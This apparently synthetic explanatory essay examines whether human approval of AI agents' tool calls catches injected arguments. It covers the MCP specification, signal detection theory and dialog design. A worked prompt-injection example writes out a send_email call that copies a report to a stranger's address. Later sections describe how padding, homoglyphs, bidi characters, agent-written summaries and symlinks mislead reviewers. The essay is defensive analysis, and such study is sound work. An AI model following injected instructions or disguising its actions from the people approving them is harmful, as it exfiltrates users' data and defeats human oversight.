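# Human approval of AI tool calls as a check on injected arguments

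## What an approval dialog asks a person to check

An AI agent is a program in which a language model carries out a task by operating other software. It may read files, search a mailbox, run commands or send messages on its user's behalf. Before some of these actions, many agents show an approval dialog, a message that asks a person to allow or refuse the action. The dialog gives that person a chance to catch the model's own mistakes and to notice if an outsider has tampered with the action.

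### How a model acts through tools

A language model produces only text, so it acts by writing a tool call, which is a request to run a named function with the values it needs, called arguments. A function that sends email takes recipients, a subject and perhaps an attachment, and one that runs shell commands takes a command string. The application around the model, called the host, finds the tool call in the model's output and decides what to do with it. The Agentic AI Foundation, an industry body, gives the desktop program Claude Desktop and the code editor Cursor as examples of hosts.

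Much of this traffic now follows the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools. An MCP server is a program that offers tools, such as a mail service or a file system. *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude*, by Anthropic, the company that makes the Claude models, reports that Anthropic's directory lists more than 950 MCP servers and that millions of people use them each day. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the current specification, describes the sequence of a tool call. The client, which is the host's connector, fetches a list of tools from the server, each with a name, a description and a schema of the arguments it accepts. The model selects a tool and fills in the arguments. The client sends the call, the server runs the function, and the result goes back to the model, which then continues.

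That loop can run without a person. Approval is a pause that the host adds after the model has written the call and before the client sends it. In OpenAI's agent toolkit for developers, for instance, the run halts until someone approves or rejects the request. If the person approves, the client sends the call and the function runs with whatever access the user has given the agent. If the person refuses, the host sends nothing to the server. It normally tells the model that the person declined, and the model may then give up, ask what was wrong or write a different call.

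### An address nobody asked for

Suppose that Ruth asks her agent to read the notes in a project folder and email the quarterly report to her colleague Tomas. One of the documents in the folder came from outside the company. It contains a passage that addresses the model instead of a human reader and directs it to copy the report to another address. The model complies, and the host now holds this call:

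```jsonc
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": [
      "tomas@example.com",
      "reports@example.net"   // <-- the value Ruth must question
    ],
    "subject": "Quarterly report",
    "attachments": ["quarterly-report.pdf"]
  }
}
```

The comment with the arrow is for the reader and would not appear in a real call. Everything except the line it marks matches Ruth's request to email this file to Tomas. The `to` field is an injected argument, meaning an argument whose value was set or changed by an attacker's text.

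MCP requires servers to validate the inputs they receive, but `reports@example.net` would also pass that check, because the field accepts email addresses and the value has the form of one. The software can't tell from this whether Ruth wants the report to go there, since she might well have a second colleague at another firm. The host asks Ruth because she knows where she wants it sent.

Security researchers call this kind of attack indirect prompt injection. The attacker leaves instructions in content that the agent will read later, and they change what the agent does. The Model Context Protocol (2026) project explained in a blog post on tool descriptions that the attack works because models follow instructions they find in content and cannot reliably tell a user's instructions from ones an attacker embedded in a web page, an email or a calendar event. OpenAI gives the example of an email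 that tricks a model into finding the user's bank statements and sharing them with the sender.

The same MCP post cites a rule of thumb from the programmer Simon Willison that three capabilities together make data theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Ruth's agent has all three, though she gave it only ordinary tools. It can read the report, it has read a stranger's document, and it can send mail. The danger comes from the combination, and users often combine tools from several servers in one session, so inspecting the email tool alone would not reveal it.

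An injection can also produce a call unrelated to the user's task, such as a deletion during a mailing job, which would at least surprise the user. The altered recipient list is less surprising because it appears in a dialog Ruth expects, about the email she asked for.

### What the protocol requires and what it leaves to the host

The MCP specification recommends human oversight in firm language but does not require it. There "SHOULD always be a human in the loop" who can deny a tool call, and applications SHOULD present confirmation prompts. Clients SHOULD also show the user a tool's inputs before calling the server, to avoid "malicious or accidental data exfiltration", as in Ruth's case. By the convention of internet standards, MUST marks an absolute requirement, while SHOULD marks a recommendation that an implementer may set aside for good reason. A host that hides the arguments, or never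 asks for approval, can therefore still conform to the protocol.

The overview that the Model Context Protocol (MCP) project drafted for the same revision has stronger wording. Like the previous revision's overview, it says hosts "must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool". However, this "must" is in lower case, and both overviews treat such words as binding only when they are capitalized. Both also acknowledge that the protocol cannot enforce its consent principles. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026), a paper on finer-grained permissions for MCP, treats the sentence as a requirement, which is a generous reading. The paper's larger point, that the protocol leaves authorization to the host, holds either way.

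Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) makes the host responsible for enforcing consent requirements and handling the user's decisions, but the specification prescribes no particular interface for doing so. The maker of the host therefore decides which calls trigger a dialog, whether the dialog shows the arguments in full, in summary or not at all, and how long the user's answer applies. Li and colleagues write that the protocol has no mechanism for tying consent to particular argument values or for revoking it. In their email example, a host offers "Allow" and "Always Allow" for the mail tool as a whole, and choosing "Always Allow" approves every later email, whatever its recipient or attachments.

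MCP gives hosts some help in deciding when to ask for approval. A server can annotate its tools, for example with a hint that a tool only reads data or that it may destroy some. According to the Model Context Protocol post, a host might skip the dialog for a read-only tool from a trusted server and require one for a destructive tool. A tool without annotations counts as potentially destructive, though hosts vary in how strictly they apply that default. The hints are only claims by the server, and a dishonest server can label a tool read-only even though it deletes data.

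An annotation describes a tool, not the values in a particular call. `send_email` has the same annotations whether the report goes to Tomas alone or to Tomas and a stranger. Annotations can therefore affect whether Ruth sees an approval dialog, but they can't alert her to the second address.

### Approval as official advice

OWASP, a non-profit that publishes widely used rankings of software risks, has one list for applications built on language models and another for agents. SC Media reported that the 2026 edition of the language-model list ranks prompt injection first and excessive agency, meaning the system has too much power, third. Superblocks' *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, a software vendor's summary, lists human approval of consequential actions among the remedies for prompt injection, alongside tighter limits on what tools can reach. According to the security vendor Aikido, the first entry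 on the agent list covers attackers who redirect an agent's goals through malicious text, and its remedies also include human approval for high-impact actions.

In OWASP's list for agents, the approving person is also a weak point. TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* describes chains of failure that start with a hijacked goal and end in human over-trust, but still includes human oversight among the recommended measures. The list has a separate entry for exploiting human trust. Auth0, an identity-software company, summarises this as using an agent's persuasive, humanlike manner to manipulate people into unsafe actions.

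OpenAI and Anthropic now differ in their guidance on approvals. OpenAI's *Safety in building agents* advises developers to always enable approvals for MCP tools, so that end users can review and confirm every operation, including reads and writes. Anthropic started from a similar position. Its programming agent, Claude Code, asked by default before it ran commands or modified files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* says that this default keeps users safe, but that people click "approve" so often that they stop paying close attention, a problem known as approval fatigue.

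Anthropic has since switched the default on several of its plans to an automated reviewer, which allows or blocks calls in the person's place. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* supports the change partly with an experiment in which human reviewers caught 13.6% of dangerous commands and the automated reviewer caught 89%. Anthropic was testing its own product, so the figures need a closer look. But if they are even roughly right, OpenAI's advice to confirm every read and write could weaken the check by increasing the number of dialogs.

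### Four conditions for stopping the call

For Ruth to stop the email by noticing the address, four things have to happen in order. Advice to "use human approval" makes this sound like a single step.

1. A dialog appears. The host pauses on this call and does not let it through on a saved permission, a read-only hint or an automated reviewer's decision.
2. The dialog displays the value. The second address is on the screen, complete and legible.
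3. Ruth reads it. She looks at the recipients, past the first name, before she clicks.
4. Ruth judges it wrong. She recognises that the address does not belong there, and she refuses.

The chance of stopping the call is then a product of conditional probabilities:

P(stop) = P(dialog appears) × P(value on screen | dialog appears) × P(person reads it | value on screen) × P(person judges it wrong | person reads it)

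The vertical bar means "given that". This formula was made for this discussion as a way to sort evidence and doesn't come from any of the works named here. The steps need not be independent, because each probability already takes the earlier steps as given. The formula assumes that someone who judges the value wrong will refuse and that the host will honour the refusal. It leaves out refusals that stop an attack by luck, as when Ruth rejects the email because of a typo in the subject line without noticing the attack.

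The product of the four probabilities can't exceed the smallest of them. To use invented numbers, if each were 0.9, the call would be blocked about 66% of the time. If Ruth reads the full recipient list in only three dialogs out of ten, she will stop at most 30% of such calls, even with a flawless display and perfect judgement. If an attacker can try ten times, a reviewer who independently stops each attempt with probability 0.9 has only about a 35% chance of stopping all ten.

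The first factor, whether a dialog appears, depends on software and settings, and researchers can study much of it by using the products. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) tested five commercial agents from Anthropic and OpenAI in May and June 2026. ChatGPT's ordinary chat mode required approval for every action that had a permission setting, and they found no way to turn this off. In its agent mode, where the model operates a remote browser, they could set no permissions, and the agent did things without approval that needed it in chat mode, such as opening Gmail. The Claude chatbot once created an email draft without asking, although they had selected "Needs approval"; the browser log showed that the system had marked the call as not requiring approval. A draft is less serious than a sent message, and products change quickly. Still, the first factor ranged from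 about one to zero within a single company's product, and a user could not have guessed which applied from the word "approval". Records of saved permissions such as "always allow" are also evidence about this factor.

An investigator can learn whether the value is on the screen by comparing what a host displays with what it then runs. This requires no human subjects, and much of the material comes from reports of display flaws. It is harder to observe whether a person reads the value, though eye-tracking and response times give some indication, and decades of work on browser warnings and mobile permission prompts offer a comparison. Approval rates from real work are weaker evidence than they look, because when nearly every request is safe, careful and careless readers will both approve nearly everything.

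Judgement can be observed separately when people have certainly looked at a value and must compare it with what they intended, as when someone checks a payee's account number before a transfer. Experiments that plant a dangerous request among harmless ones usually measure reading and judgement together. When every planted request reaches a complete, legible dialog, the first two factors equal one, and the catch rate, the share of dangerous requests that people refuse, estimates the product of reading and judgement plus any lucky refusals. The false alarm rate, the share of safe requests that people refuse, gives some idea of how common lucky refusals are. A low catch rate alone does not show whether people skipped the address or read it and found nothing odd. Fewer or more conspicuous dialogs might help a person who skipped it, but someone who read `reports@example.net` and took it for a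 shared company mailbox needs information that the address does not contain.

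## Why a malicious value is hard to recognise: what theory predicts

Even if the host's dialog shows the whole call and Ruth reads every character, she may still approve sending the report to a stranger.

### What a careful reader still has to know

To judge an argument, a person compares it with what she intended. Ruth can do this for an email because she named the recipient herself. But people often use agents to avoid deciding such details. Someone who asks an agent to repair a failing software build wants the build fixed but has no particular package to install or folder to clear in mind. When a dialog shows her a package name, she can only judge whether it is plausible, and an attacker can choose a plausible name.

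It would also help Ruth to know where the value came from. She mentioned Tomas, but the second address came from an outsider's document. If she had known that, she would have been suspicious even without finding out who owns the mailbox. The call lists both addresses in the same format, though, and doesn't record their sources. Showing the user's request next to the call partly fixes this. The automated reviewers in *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026), a paper on authorising agents' actions, receive the user's exact request along with the action awaiting approval, so they can at least detect that the user named one recipient and the call has two.

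Finally, the reader has to know what the value refers to. Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, analysed 290 public reports of agents misusing files. They note that a dialog for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, yet approving it lets whatever code is in that script run. `cargo build`, which compiles a program, also runs build scripts that come with other people's packages. A malicious package could use one to read the user's login key while the dialog shows only the build command. The team attributed 31 of the reports partly to uninformative approvals. People post such reports after something goes wrong, so we can't calculate a rate from the count, and only 21 of the 290 involved prompt injection. But a user who can't see what a script does has the same problem whether the model erred or an attacker steered it.

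Links and paths have the same weakness. A shortened link shows the name of the shortening service, which supplies the real destination only when someone opens the link. A path such as `../shared/config` leads to different files depending on the folder where the command starts, and a folder in the path may be a pointer to somewhere else on the disk. Anthropic gives the example of `git push`, which uploads code to a repository. The same command can be routine or a leak depending on whether the repository is private or public, so even an expert could not judge it from the text alone. Anthropic's automated reviewer now looks up which it is first, but a person would have to leave the dialog to do so.

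### Cranor's framework for human failure

Security researchers had a way to classify such failures long before AI agents existed. Cranor, in *A Framework for Reasoning About the Human in the Loop*, treats a security message as a communication that should lead a person to act, and lists what can go wrong. The person must notice the message and pay attention to it long enough to take it in. She must understand it, know what to do about it, apply what she has learned to the case at hand, and be capable of the task. Her expertise, beliefs and motivation affect the result, as do distractions and attackers who interfere with the message.

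Cranor added capability as a factor to an older model from research on warnings because she had seen people blamed for failing at tasks they could not do. Ruth's problem with an unfamiliar address is one of capability.

The framework also separates warnings from notices. A warning alerts people to a hazard and should tell them how to avoid it, while a notice describes something and leaves the judgement to them. An approval dialog interrupts Ruth as a warning would, but usually gives her no evidence of a hazard. It only describes the call, as a notice does, because the host has no particular reason to think the call is dangerous.

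Cranor's framework includes a type of error that the psychologist James Reason calls a "mistake", in which a person correctly carries out a sensible plan that doesn't work. Her example is a user who opens attachments only from people he knows, and then receives a worm from a friend's infected computer. Checking that a recipient "looks like one of ours" is a similar plan, and it fails when an attacker registers a similar name.

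Cranor advises automating a decision when software is likely to make it better than a person would, and leaving people the decisions that depend on context a computer lacks. With tool calls, Ruth and the host each have part of the context. Ruth knows whom she meant to write to, and the host has the session log showing which document the address came from. This suggests that the host should show Ruth its part before asking her to decide. Cranor's framework is a checklist with the relations between its parts left vague on purpose, and it offers no way to calculate how often a reader will fail.

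### Sensitivity and criterion

Psychologists use signal detection theory to analyse yes-or-no decisions made on uncertain evidence. The theory assumes that each request arouses some degree of suspicion in the reader. Malicious requests arouse more on average than safe ones, but the two ranges overlap. The reader refuses whenever her suspicion passes a threshold, called the criterion. She can err by approving a malicious request, which is a miss, or by refusing a safe one, which is a false alarm.

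How far apart the two ranges lie is her sensitivity, written d′. If both follow bell curves of equal width, the catch rate H and the false-alarm rate F are enough to calculate sensitivity and the criterion c:

d′ = z(H) − z(F)

c = −½ [z(H) + z(F)]

Here z(p) is the point on a standard bell curve with a proportion p of the area to its left, so z(0.5) is 0 and z(0.02) is about −2.05. A reader who can't tell the two kinds of request apart has a d′ of 0. A positive c means she leans towards approval.

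Human reviewers in Anthropic's experiment caught 13.6% of malicious requests. If they also refused 2% of safe ones, an invented figure, their sensitivity would be about 0.96 and their criterion about 1.58, meaning that they discriminate poorly and lean heavily towards approval. If they became more willing to refuse but learned nothing new about the requests, they would have to refuse about 17% of the safe ones to catch half of the malicious ones. To catch 89%, the automated reviewer's rate in the same experiment, they would have to refuse about 61% of the safe ones. Telling reviewers to be more careful therefore helps only if it leads them to find something out, such as where a link goes.

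The theory also has a rule for where a rational reader should set the criterion. She should refuse when the evidence is more likely under an attack than under a safe request by at least this factor:

(safe requests ÷ malicious requests) × (cost of a false alarm ÷ cost of a miss)

If one request in 5,000 is an attack and a miss is 100 times as bad as a false alarm, rejecting a request is worthwhile only when the evidence is at least about 50 times as likely under an attack as under a legitimate request. A reader with a sensitivity (d′) of 0.96 would almost never see evidence that strong, so approving nearly everything can be a reasonable response to weak evidence and rare attacks.

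### People miss what they seldom see

In *Rare targets are often missed in visual search*, Wolfe, Horowitz and Kenner (2005) asked volunteers to look for a tool in cluttered images of overlapping, semi-transparent objects. The volunteers missed 7% of the tools when half of the images contained one and 30% when 1% did, an increase known as the low-prevalence effect. They also answered more quickly that no tool was there when tools were rare.

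Two years later, Fleck and Mitroff reproduced the result in *Rare Targets Are Rarely Missed in Correctable Search* but disputed what it meant. Twenty young adults each searched 1,400 displays for a tool, which was present in 50%, 10% or 2% of displays, depending on the block. Ten people could not change their answers, and they missed 10%, 19% and 31% of the tools at those three rates. The other ten could press a key to reverse their previous answer, and they missed 4%, 10% and 10%. Before corrections, they had missed 8%, 19% and 27%. Fleck and Mitroff concluded that people had often seen the tool but answered too fast. With only ten people in a group, though, the remaining rise from 4% to 10% could be a real effect that the study was too small to detect. Correction also works only when the action can be reversed. If Ruth notices the second address just after she clicks, it helps her only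 if the host has not yet sent the email.

Further experiments by Wolfe's group suggested that haste was only part of the cause, since misses stayed fairly high when the experimenters penalised fast answers. *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance* reports that the group also tried other changes, such as having two people search together, but only bursts of frequent targets with feedback raised detection of rare targets. These bursts also raised false alarms, as a shift in criterion would. *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering* (Dewis, Hout and colleagues, 2026) has since attributed most of the misses to drifting attention.

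The largest synthesis so far, *The role of feedback in the low-prevalence effect* (Caruso, Fox and colleagues, 2026), suggests that people miss rare targets mainly because their criterion shifts, rather than because their sensitivity falls. Across 62 comparisons from 29 publications, rarity shifted people towards answering "absent" by 1.80 standard deviations, while its effect on sensitivity was small and statistically indistinguishable from zero. Professionals did not differ reliably from novices. The 1.80 is probably too high, because smaller studies reported larger shifts, a possible sign of publication bias, and the team could obtain usable data for fewer than half of the roughly 140 eligible effects. The low-prevalence effect also occurs in clinical work. According to *Even expert mammographers can miss breast cancer cases*, a news report on a study by Evans, Birdwell and Wolfe, specialists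 missed 30% of cancers in the clinic but 12% of the same cancers in a set where cancer was common.

The effect is less certain to carry over to approval dialogs. Caruso and colleagues found a larger shift when experimenters told people after each trial whether they had been right. Ruth gets almost no such feedback, since a successful theft of her report looks like a sent email. In some experiments where people sort items into categories without feedback, rarity has the opposite effect, and people begin to count more borderline cases as members of the rare category. Reviewing a tool call involves both searching the fields for an odd value and categorising that value as odd enough to refuse or not. I think that the search experiments are the better guide for long calls, and that even the direction of the effect is uncertain for short, ambiguous ones.

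Laboratory results may also overstate how well reviewers would do, because a volunteer looking for a tool knows what tools look like, while Ruth has to watch for anything wrong. In *How did I miss that?*, a study of errors in radiology, observers missed 5% of the specific objects they were looking for, but 37.5% of targets defined only by a category when those were the rarer kind. How rarely each type of target appears also matters. The Association for Psychological Science's *Super Rare Items Are Most Likely to Be Missed* describes a screening game with 78 illegal items. Players spotted 92% of the items that appeared more than 1% of the time, but only 27% of those that appeared less than 0.15% of the time. A user who had learned to spot one kind of injected argument might still do badly with an unfamiliar kind.

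### One attack in 5,000 dialogs

When attacks are rare, a refusal is weak evidence of an attack, even if rarity doesn't change how people behave. Assume 5,000 dialogs, one of them malicious, with the same catch rate of 13.6% and false-alarm rate of 2%. Only the catch rate comes from an experiment, and none of these figures describes a real group of users. The reader would refuse about 100 safe requests (4,999 × 0.02) and catch 0.136 attacks on average, or roughly 735 false alarms per catch. The attack would get through about 86% of the time.

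The table changes the inputs. In the last row, the reader refuses more readily but is no better at telling safe from malicious.

| Case | Attacks | Catch rate | False-alarm rate | Safe requests refused | Attacks caught | False alarms per catch |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Starting assumptions | 1 | 13.6% | 2% | 100 | 0.136 | 735 |
| Higher catch rate | 1 | 89% | 2% | 100 | 0.89 | 112 |
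| Fewer false alarms | 1 | 13.6% | 0.2% | 10 | 0.136 | 74 |
| More attacks | 10 | 13.6% | 2% | 100 | 1.36 | 73 |
| Stricter reader, same sensitivity | 1 | 50% | 17% | 850 | 0.5 | 1,700 |

The number of false alarms per catch depends mostly on the frequency of attacks and the false-alarm rate, because either can change by a factor of ten or a hundred. Even a perfect catch rate would only bring the number down to 100. The chance that a given attack succeeds depends only on the catch rate, so cutting false alarms tenfold stops no additional attacks. A lower ratio of false alarms to catches also doesn't mean that fewer attacks succeed. The ratio is much lower in the row with ten attacks than in the row with one, but between eight and nine of the ten attacks succeed.

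The second row is harder to reach than it looks, because a reader can't get there just by trying harder. Catching 89% of attacks at a false-alarm rate of 2% requires a sensitivity of about 3.3, more than three times the starting value.

Some false alarms come from requests that are safe but odd. *Approve What, Exactly?* tests its reviewers with a set of these: a large payment the user did ask for, two recipients the user did name, and a strangely written but harmless file path. A rule such as "refuse any email with an extra recipient" would have protected Ruth's report, but it would also block every email she means to send to two people.

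### Predictions that experiments can test

If the low-prevalence effect carries over, catch rates should fall as attacks become rarer. An experimenter could test this by changing only the share of dialogs that contain the malicious request. If readers merely became less willing to reject requests (a shift in criterion), catches and false alarms would fall together. If catches fell while false alarms held steady or rose, readers would have become worse at telling malicious requests from safe ones. A study in which half of the dialogs are malicious would probably overstate how well people catch attacks at work.

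Theory also predicts that reviewers will catch a smaller share of attacks as approval dialogs repeat, even if attacks stay equally common. Cranor lists habituation, the weakening response to a familiar stimulus, among the reasons people stop noticing security messages. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) applies the idea to agents by treating a reviewer's attention as a limited resource that each approval request uses up, so a system that asks five hundred times a day gets less scrutiny per request than one that asks five times. The paper assumes this fatigue in a model and includes no observations of people, so the prediction still needs to be tested by comparing how often reviewers catch the same malicious request early and late in a session.

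The last prediction is that people will catch fewer malicious values when these resemble legitimate ones. *No evidence of attentional prioritization for threatening targets in visual search* summarises the current theory that, when targets are rare, people detect only the most visible or typical examples. The address `reports@example.net` isn't a typical danger in the way that a command erasing a home directory is. Resemblance should lower sensitivity, the ability to tell malicious values from legitimate ones, so refusing more readily would bring more false alarms without restoring the earlier balance between misses and false alarms. Unlike a tumour, a malicious address can be designed to escape notice, for example by resembling a colleague's. An experiment that plants only blatant commands would therefore overstate the chance that Ruth stops her email.

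## Whether the dialog shows the whole argument

Ruth can only question the second address if the dialog puts it on her screen. A careless host might present her email like this:

```text
The assistant wants to send an email
"Sending the quarterly report to Tomas, as you asked."

To: tomas@example.com +1 more          [Show details]

[Allow]   [Refuse]
```

Nothing here is false, since Tomas will get the report. But the host has folded away the one value Ruth needs to see, and the sentence in quotation marks comes from the model, which was already following the attacker's text when it wrote the call. A better dialog for the same call might look like this:

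```text
send_email

To (2):        tomas@example.com
               reports@example.net
Subject:       Quarterly report
Body:          (empty)
Attachment:    quarterly-report.pdf
Actual file:   /home/ruth/finance/quarterly-report.pdf

[Allow]   [Refuse]
```

This display is faithful, meaning that it shows the complete action that will run, in readable form. But nothing in it indicates that the second address belongs to a stranger.

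### Long values and blank space

Hosts have good reason to shorten values, because an agent that creates a file passes the whole content as one argument. That argument can run to thousands of lines, and a dialog may have room for ten. Some hosts cut off long values after a fixed length, and others fold them behind a link such as "Show details". Either way, the person sees only the beginning. If a dialog shows the first 80 characters of a 400-character command, the person sees a fifth of it, and an attacker who influences the command also influences what that fifth contains.

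Blank space can also hide part of an argument, even when the host shortens nothing. Enough of it inside a value pushes the rest out of view, so the person sees what looks like a short, complete command. *What You Approve Is What Executes* (Weng, 2026), a paper on approval dialogs for AI agents, lists this padding among the known ways to misrepresent an action. It is arguably worse than truncation because it leaves no sign that anything is missing, whereas a shortened value usually ends in an ellipsis or a link.

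A host should always show recipients, paths and web addresses in full. If it folds something long, such as the body of an email, it should state how much it has hidden. Shell commands are harder to shorten safely because any part of one can do damage. Long runs of blank space need a visible marker, such as "[212 spaces]". In a dialog, a marker is safer than deletion because file names can contain spaces, and removing them would display the name of a different file. Weng's software strips padding before it analyses a command, which is reasonable for analysis.

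Users won't read 3,000 lines in a dialog, though, even if it shows the whole argument. For an edit to an existing file, the host can show only the changed lines, as code-review tools do. But every line of a new file is new, so a complete display of a large one will be too long to read.

### Characters that mislead the eye

Even a short value can look different from what it is. Unicode is the standard that gives every character in the world's writing systems a number, and *Unicode Source Code Handling* (Leroy and Davis, 2024) sets out its guidance for programming tools. The basic problem it addresses is that two different lines of code can look the same on the screen. Leroy and Davis had code reviewers in mind, but a person reading an approval dialog is in the same position.

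Some letters look identical, such as the Latin, Greek and Cyrillic capital A. In an example by Leroy and Davis, a short program appears to set every cell in a table to zero but clears only the diagonal, because one letter "i" is Cyrillic. The same substitution in an email address would show Ruth a colleague's name but send the report to someone else, and she could not detect it however carefully she read. The host has to detect it for her, for instance by marking any address that mixes alphabets within a word. The Unicode Consortium publishes mechanisms for detecting such problems. A host should not flag every Cyrillic address, or people who write in Cyrillic will learn to ignore the mark.

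Text direction causes subtler problems. Arabic and Hebrew run from right to left, but the digits within them run from left to right, so software stores characters in what the Unicode Consortium calls logical order and rearranges them for display. Some invisible characters affect how they are rearranged. Leroy and Davis show a line of code that appears to shift a number's bits to the right but actually shifts them to the left.

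A host cannot solve the problem by banning the invisible direction characters, because another of the examples contains none. It looks like a loop through the Hebrew alphabet but does nothing, because the screen shows the two ends of the range in reverse. Forcing every character into left-to-right order also fails, because it makes Arabic illegible or changes what it appears to say. Leroy and Davis recommend dividing the text into the units of its language, such as names, operators and strings, and keeping those units in a fixed order, so that the usual direction rules apply only inside each unit.

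This matters for tool calls because hosts commonly hold the arguments as JSON, the name-and-value format used for Ruth's call earlier. In one of the standard's examples, right-to-left text inside JSON makes a value look like the name of a different field. A host can avoid most of this confusion by printing each argument on its own line, under its own label, and isolating each value's text direction.

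Programs also differ in which characters they treat as line breaks. A person may see two lines where the program running the text reads only one, so a safety check that appears on the second line is part of a comment and never runs. Conversely, text that looks like a comment can run as code. Leroy and Davis advise editors to display every recognised line break as a break and never to remove one. A host should do the same, and mark any break that the program receiving the command would interpret differently.

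Other characters have no visible form. A variation selector, for example, picks between versions of the character before it, such as a plain symbol and a colour emoji. Software normally ignores a selector it doesn't support, which lets people hide data in ordinary-looking text. Freytag, Davis and Scherer (2026), in *Make sequences with multiple variation selectors in a row formally non-conformant*, proposed a change to the Unicode standard partly for this reason, and they name prompt injection among the possible abuses. Under their proposal, software would display a misplaced invisible character as a missing glyph, the mark shown in place of a character the software cannot draw. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode® 18.0.0 (DRAFT)* (2026) lists new requirements on variation selectors.

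Under the proposal, many invisible characters would stay hidden when they appear in permitted positions. Freytag and colleagues also mention a "Show Hidden" option, which gives invisible characters and confusable spaces a visible symbol. An approval dialog should turn this option on by default. A person about to allow a command needs to know that it contains something she cannot see, and she would have no reason to look for the option herself.

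Many coding agents run in a terminal, which treats some character sequences as instructions to change colour, move the cursor or erase text. If the host prints an argument unchanged, the argument can alter the display around it. The person then reads the altered screen, but the tool runs with the original argument. The host should print every control character as a visible symbol.

Developers looking for official advice on this may first find the Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Security Considerations*. The Consortium has not maintained that report since 2014 and warns that its recommendations may conflict with newer standards.

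### A summary written by the agent

The sentence about Tomas in the first dialog shows a different weakness. Weng argues that current agents write the text of their own approval dialogs, so the person approves a description from a component that an attacker may control. Researchers at the security firm Checkmarx showed in 2025 that a compromised agent can present a harmless description while it runs something else. According to Weng, the vendors who received the report classed the problem as outside their threat models, the sets of attacks their products are supposed to withstand.

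When the dialog shows the agent's summary, the person sees a fluent sentence that matches her request and misses whatever it leaves out. For example, "Sending the quarterly report to Tomas" is accurate even if the call also sends the report to a second recipient. The host should therefore write the description itself, from the arguments in the call. If the host also shows the agent's explanation, it should label that explanation as the agent's and keep it separate from the host's description.

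Some hosts might prefer to drop the explanation, but that would hurt people who can't read shell commands, because an honest agent's summary may be the only part of the dialog they understand. Labelling the explanation is a compromise, since someone can still read the friendly summary and skip the command below it.

Weng probably overstates how much dialogs depend on the agent's summary. Many hosts show the actual command or file name, as in the `python3 setup.py` dialogs that Zhong and colleagues discuss. Weng did not test commercial agents, so has no figure for how many rely on summaries. A dialog that shows the exact argument can also mislead the user.

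### A path that leads somewhere else

Programmers routinely use symbolic links, which are file system entries that redirect to another file. If a project folder contains one, an agent may ask to edit a settings file in that folder but actually change a file elsewhere on the machine. The person approving the edit sees the name of the settings file but doesn't see which file will change.

According to Infosecurity Magazine's *GhostApproval Flaw Hits Six Major AI Coding Assistants*, the security company Wiz reported in July 2026 that hostile projects could exploit links of this kind in six coding assistants: Amazon Q Developer, Claude Code, Augment, Cursor, Google Antigravity and Windsurf. In several of them, the agent had identified the sensitive file it was about to change, but the dialog showed only the harmless name. Wiz advised vendors to resolve links before asking for approval and to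 flag any write outside the project.

Two of the resulting fixes have entries in CVE, the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. AWS's *CVE-2026-12957 and CVE-2026-12958* (2026), a bulletin from Amazon's cloud business, attributes the second flaw to a missing check on links in the software behind Amazon Q's editor plug-ins. AWS fixed it in version 1.69.0 of that software and offered no workaround for people who could not update. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-12958* (2026), an entry in an open vulnerability database, the flaw could allow a file write outside the folder the user had trusted, and its severity is 8.5 out of 10.

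Cursor's flaw was different because the user would have seen no dialog at all, which fails the first condition, that a dialog appears. According to *CVE-2026-50549 Detail* in NVD, the US government's vulnerability database, Cursor checked where a path really led before writing a file, but if that check failed, it used the original path and wrote without approval. The flaw had a severity score of 9.3, and Cursor fixed it in version 3.0. A host that can't determine where a path leads should refuse the write, or at least tell the user so and ask for approval.

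Both entries describe the problem as link following, and neither mentions a misleading dialog. The fixes show that Amazon and Cursor accept responsibility for keeping writes inside the project. It is less clear whether they also accept responsibility for showing the true target in the dialog.

Resolving the path does not show what a script at that path would do. One experiment presented players of a game with this problem. Saved rules have a similar limit. Anthropic notes in its Claude Code documentation that a rule to block a command matches the command as written. It directs users who need to control network access regardless of the wording to a sandbox, a restricted environment for running programs.

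### Whether a misleading dialog is a flaw

The six vendors disagreed about whether Wiz had found a vulnerability. Infosecurity Magazine reports that Amazon, Google and Cursor treated the finding as one and released fixes. Augment and Windsurf acknowledged the report but had no fix by the time of publication. Anthropic disputed that Claude Code's behaviour was a vulnerability. It said the scenario was "outside our threat model" because a user who trusts a folder and then approves an edit is responsible for that decision.

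That position is consistent with what the company tells its users. Claude Code shows a trust dialog when someone starts it in a folder she has not trusted before, and Anthropic states in its security documentation that users are responsible for reviewing proposed code and commands before they approve them. A reasonable argument for the position is that a hostile project can harm a developer in many ways besides links once she runs its code. No host can check for all of them, so a vendor couldn't keep a promise to take responsibility for every hostile project.

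Anthropic may also have done more than its reply suggests. Forkast, a news site that credits its articles to "minds" and may publish machine-written text, reports that Anthropic had updated the dialog to warn about links shortly before it received Wiz's report. That would be an important point in Anthropic's favour, but it needs a better source.

Wiz objected that the design bypasses informed consent. A user can review only what the dialog shows her, and approving an edit to a project file is a different decision from approving an edit to the file that controls logins to her machine. Anthropic's security documentation also describes write operations as "strictly confined to the project scope", and a user who has read that has less reason to suspect a familiar file name. The company has fixed at least one such problem itself. Snyk's *UNIX Symbolic Link (Symlink) Following* (2026), an entry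 in a security firm's database, describes another flaw in Claude Code that let an attacker use links to write outside the workspace, and it lists version 2.1.64 as the fix.

The other flaw in AWS's bulletin let commands in a project's configuration files run automatically, but only after the user had agreed to trust the folder. AWS issued a fix, although by Anthropic's reasoning the user might have been responsible for the decision to trust the folder too. AWS does expect customers to share responsibility for security. In an earlier bulletin, AWS (2025) presented human approval as one of its products' safeguards and recommended that customers choose their own controls.

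The dispute is easier to settle for links than for hostile projects in general. The host can look up a link's target in a single operation, far more easily than the user can, so it makes sense to hold the host responsible for displaying the real target. The user remains responsible for whatever the host cannot determine, such as whether Ruth has a colleague at example.net.

### A change after the click

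A dialog that is accurate when the person reads it can be wrong by the time the action runs. The agent might substitute another call after the approval, or someone might alter a file that the approved command uses. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use problem. Better layout can't help, because the change happens after the person has read the dialog.

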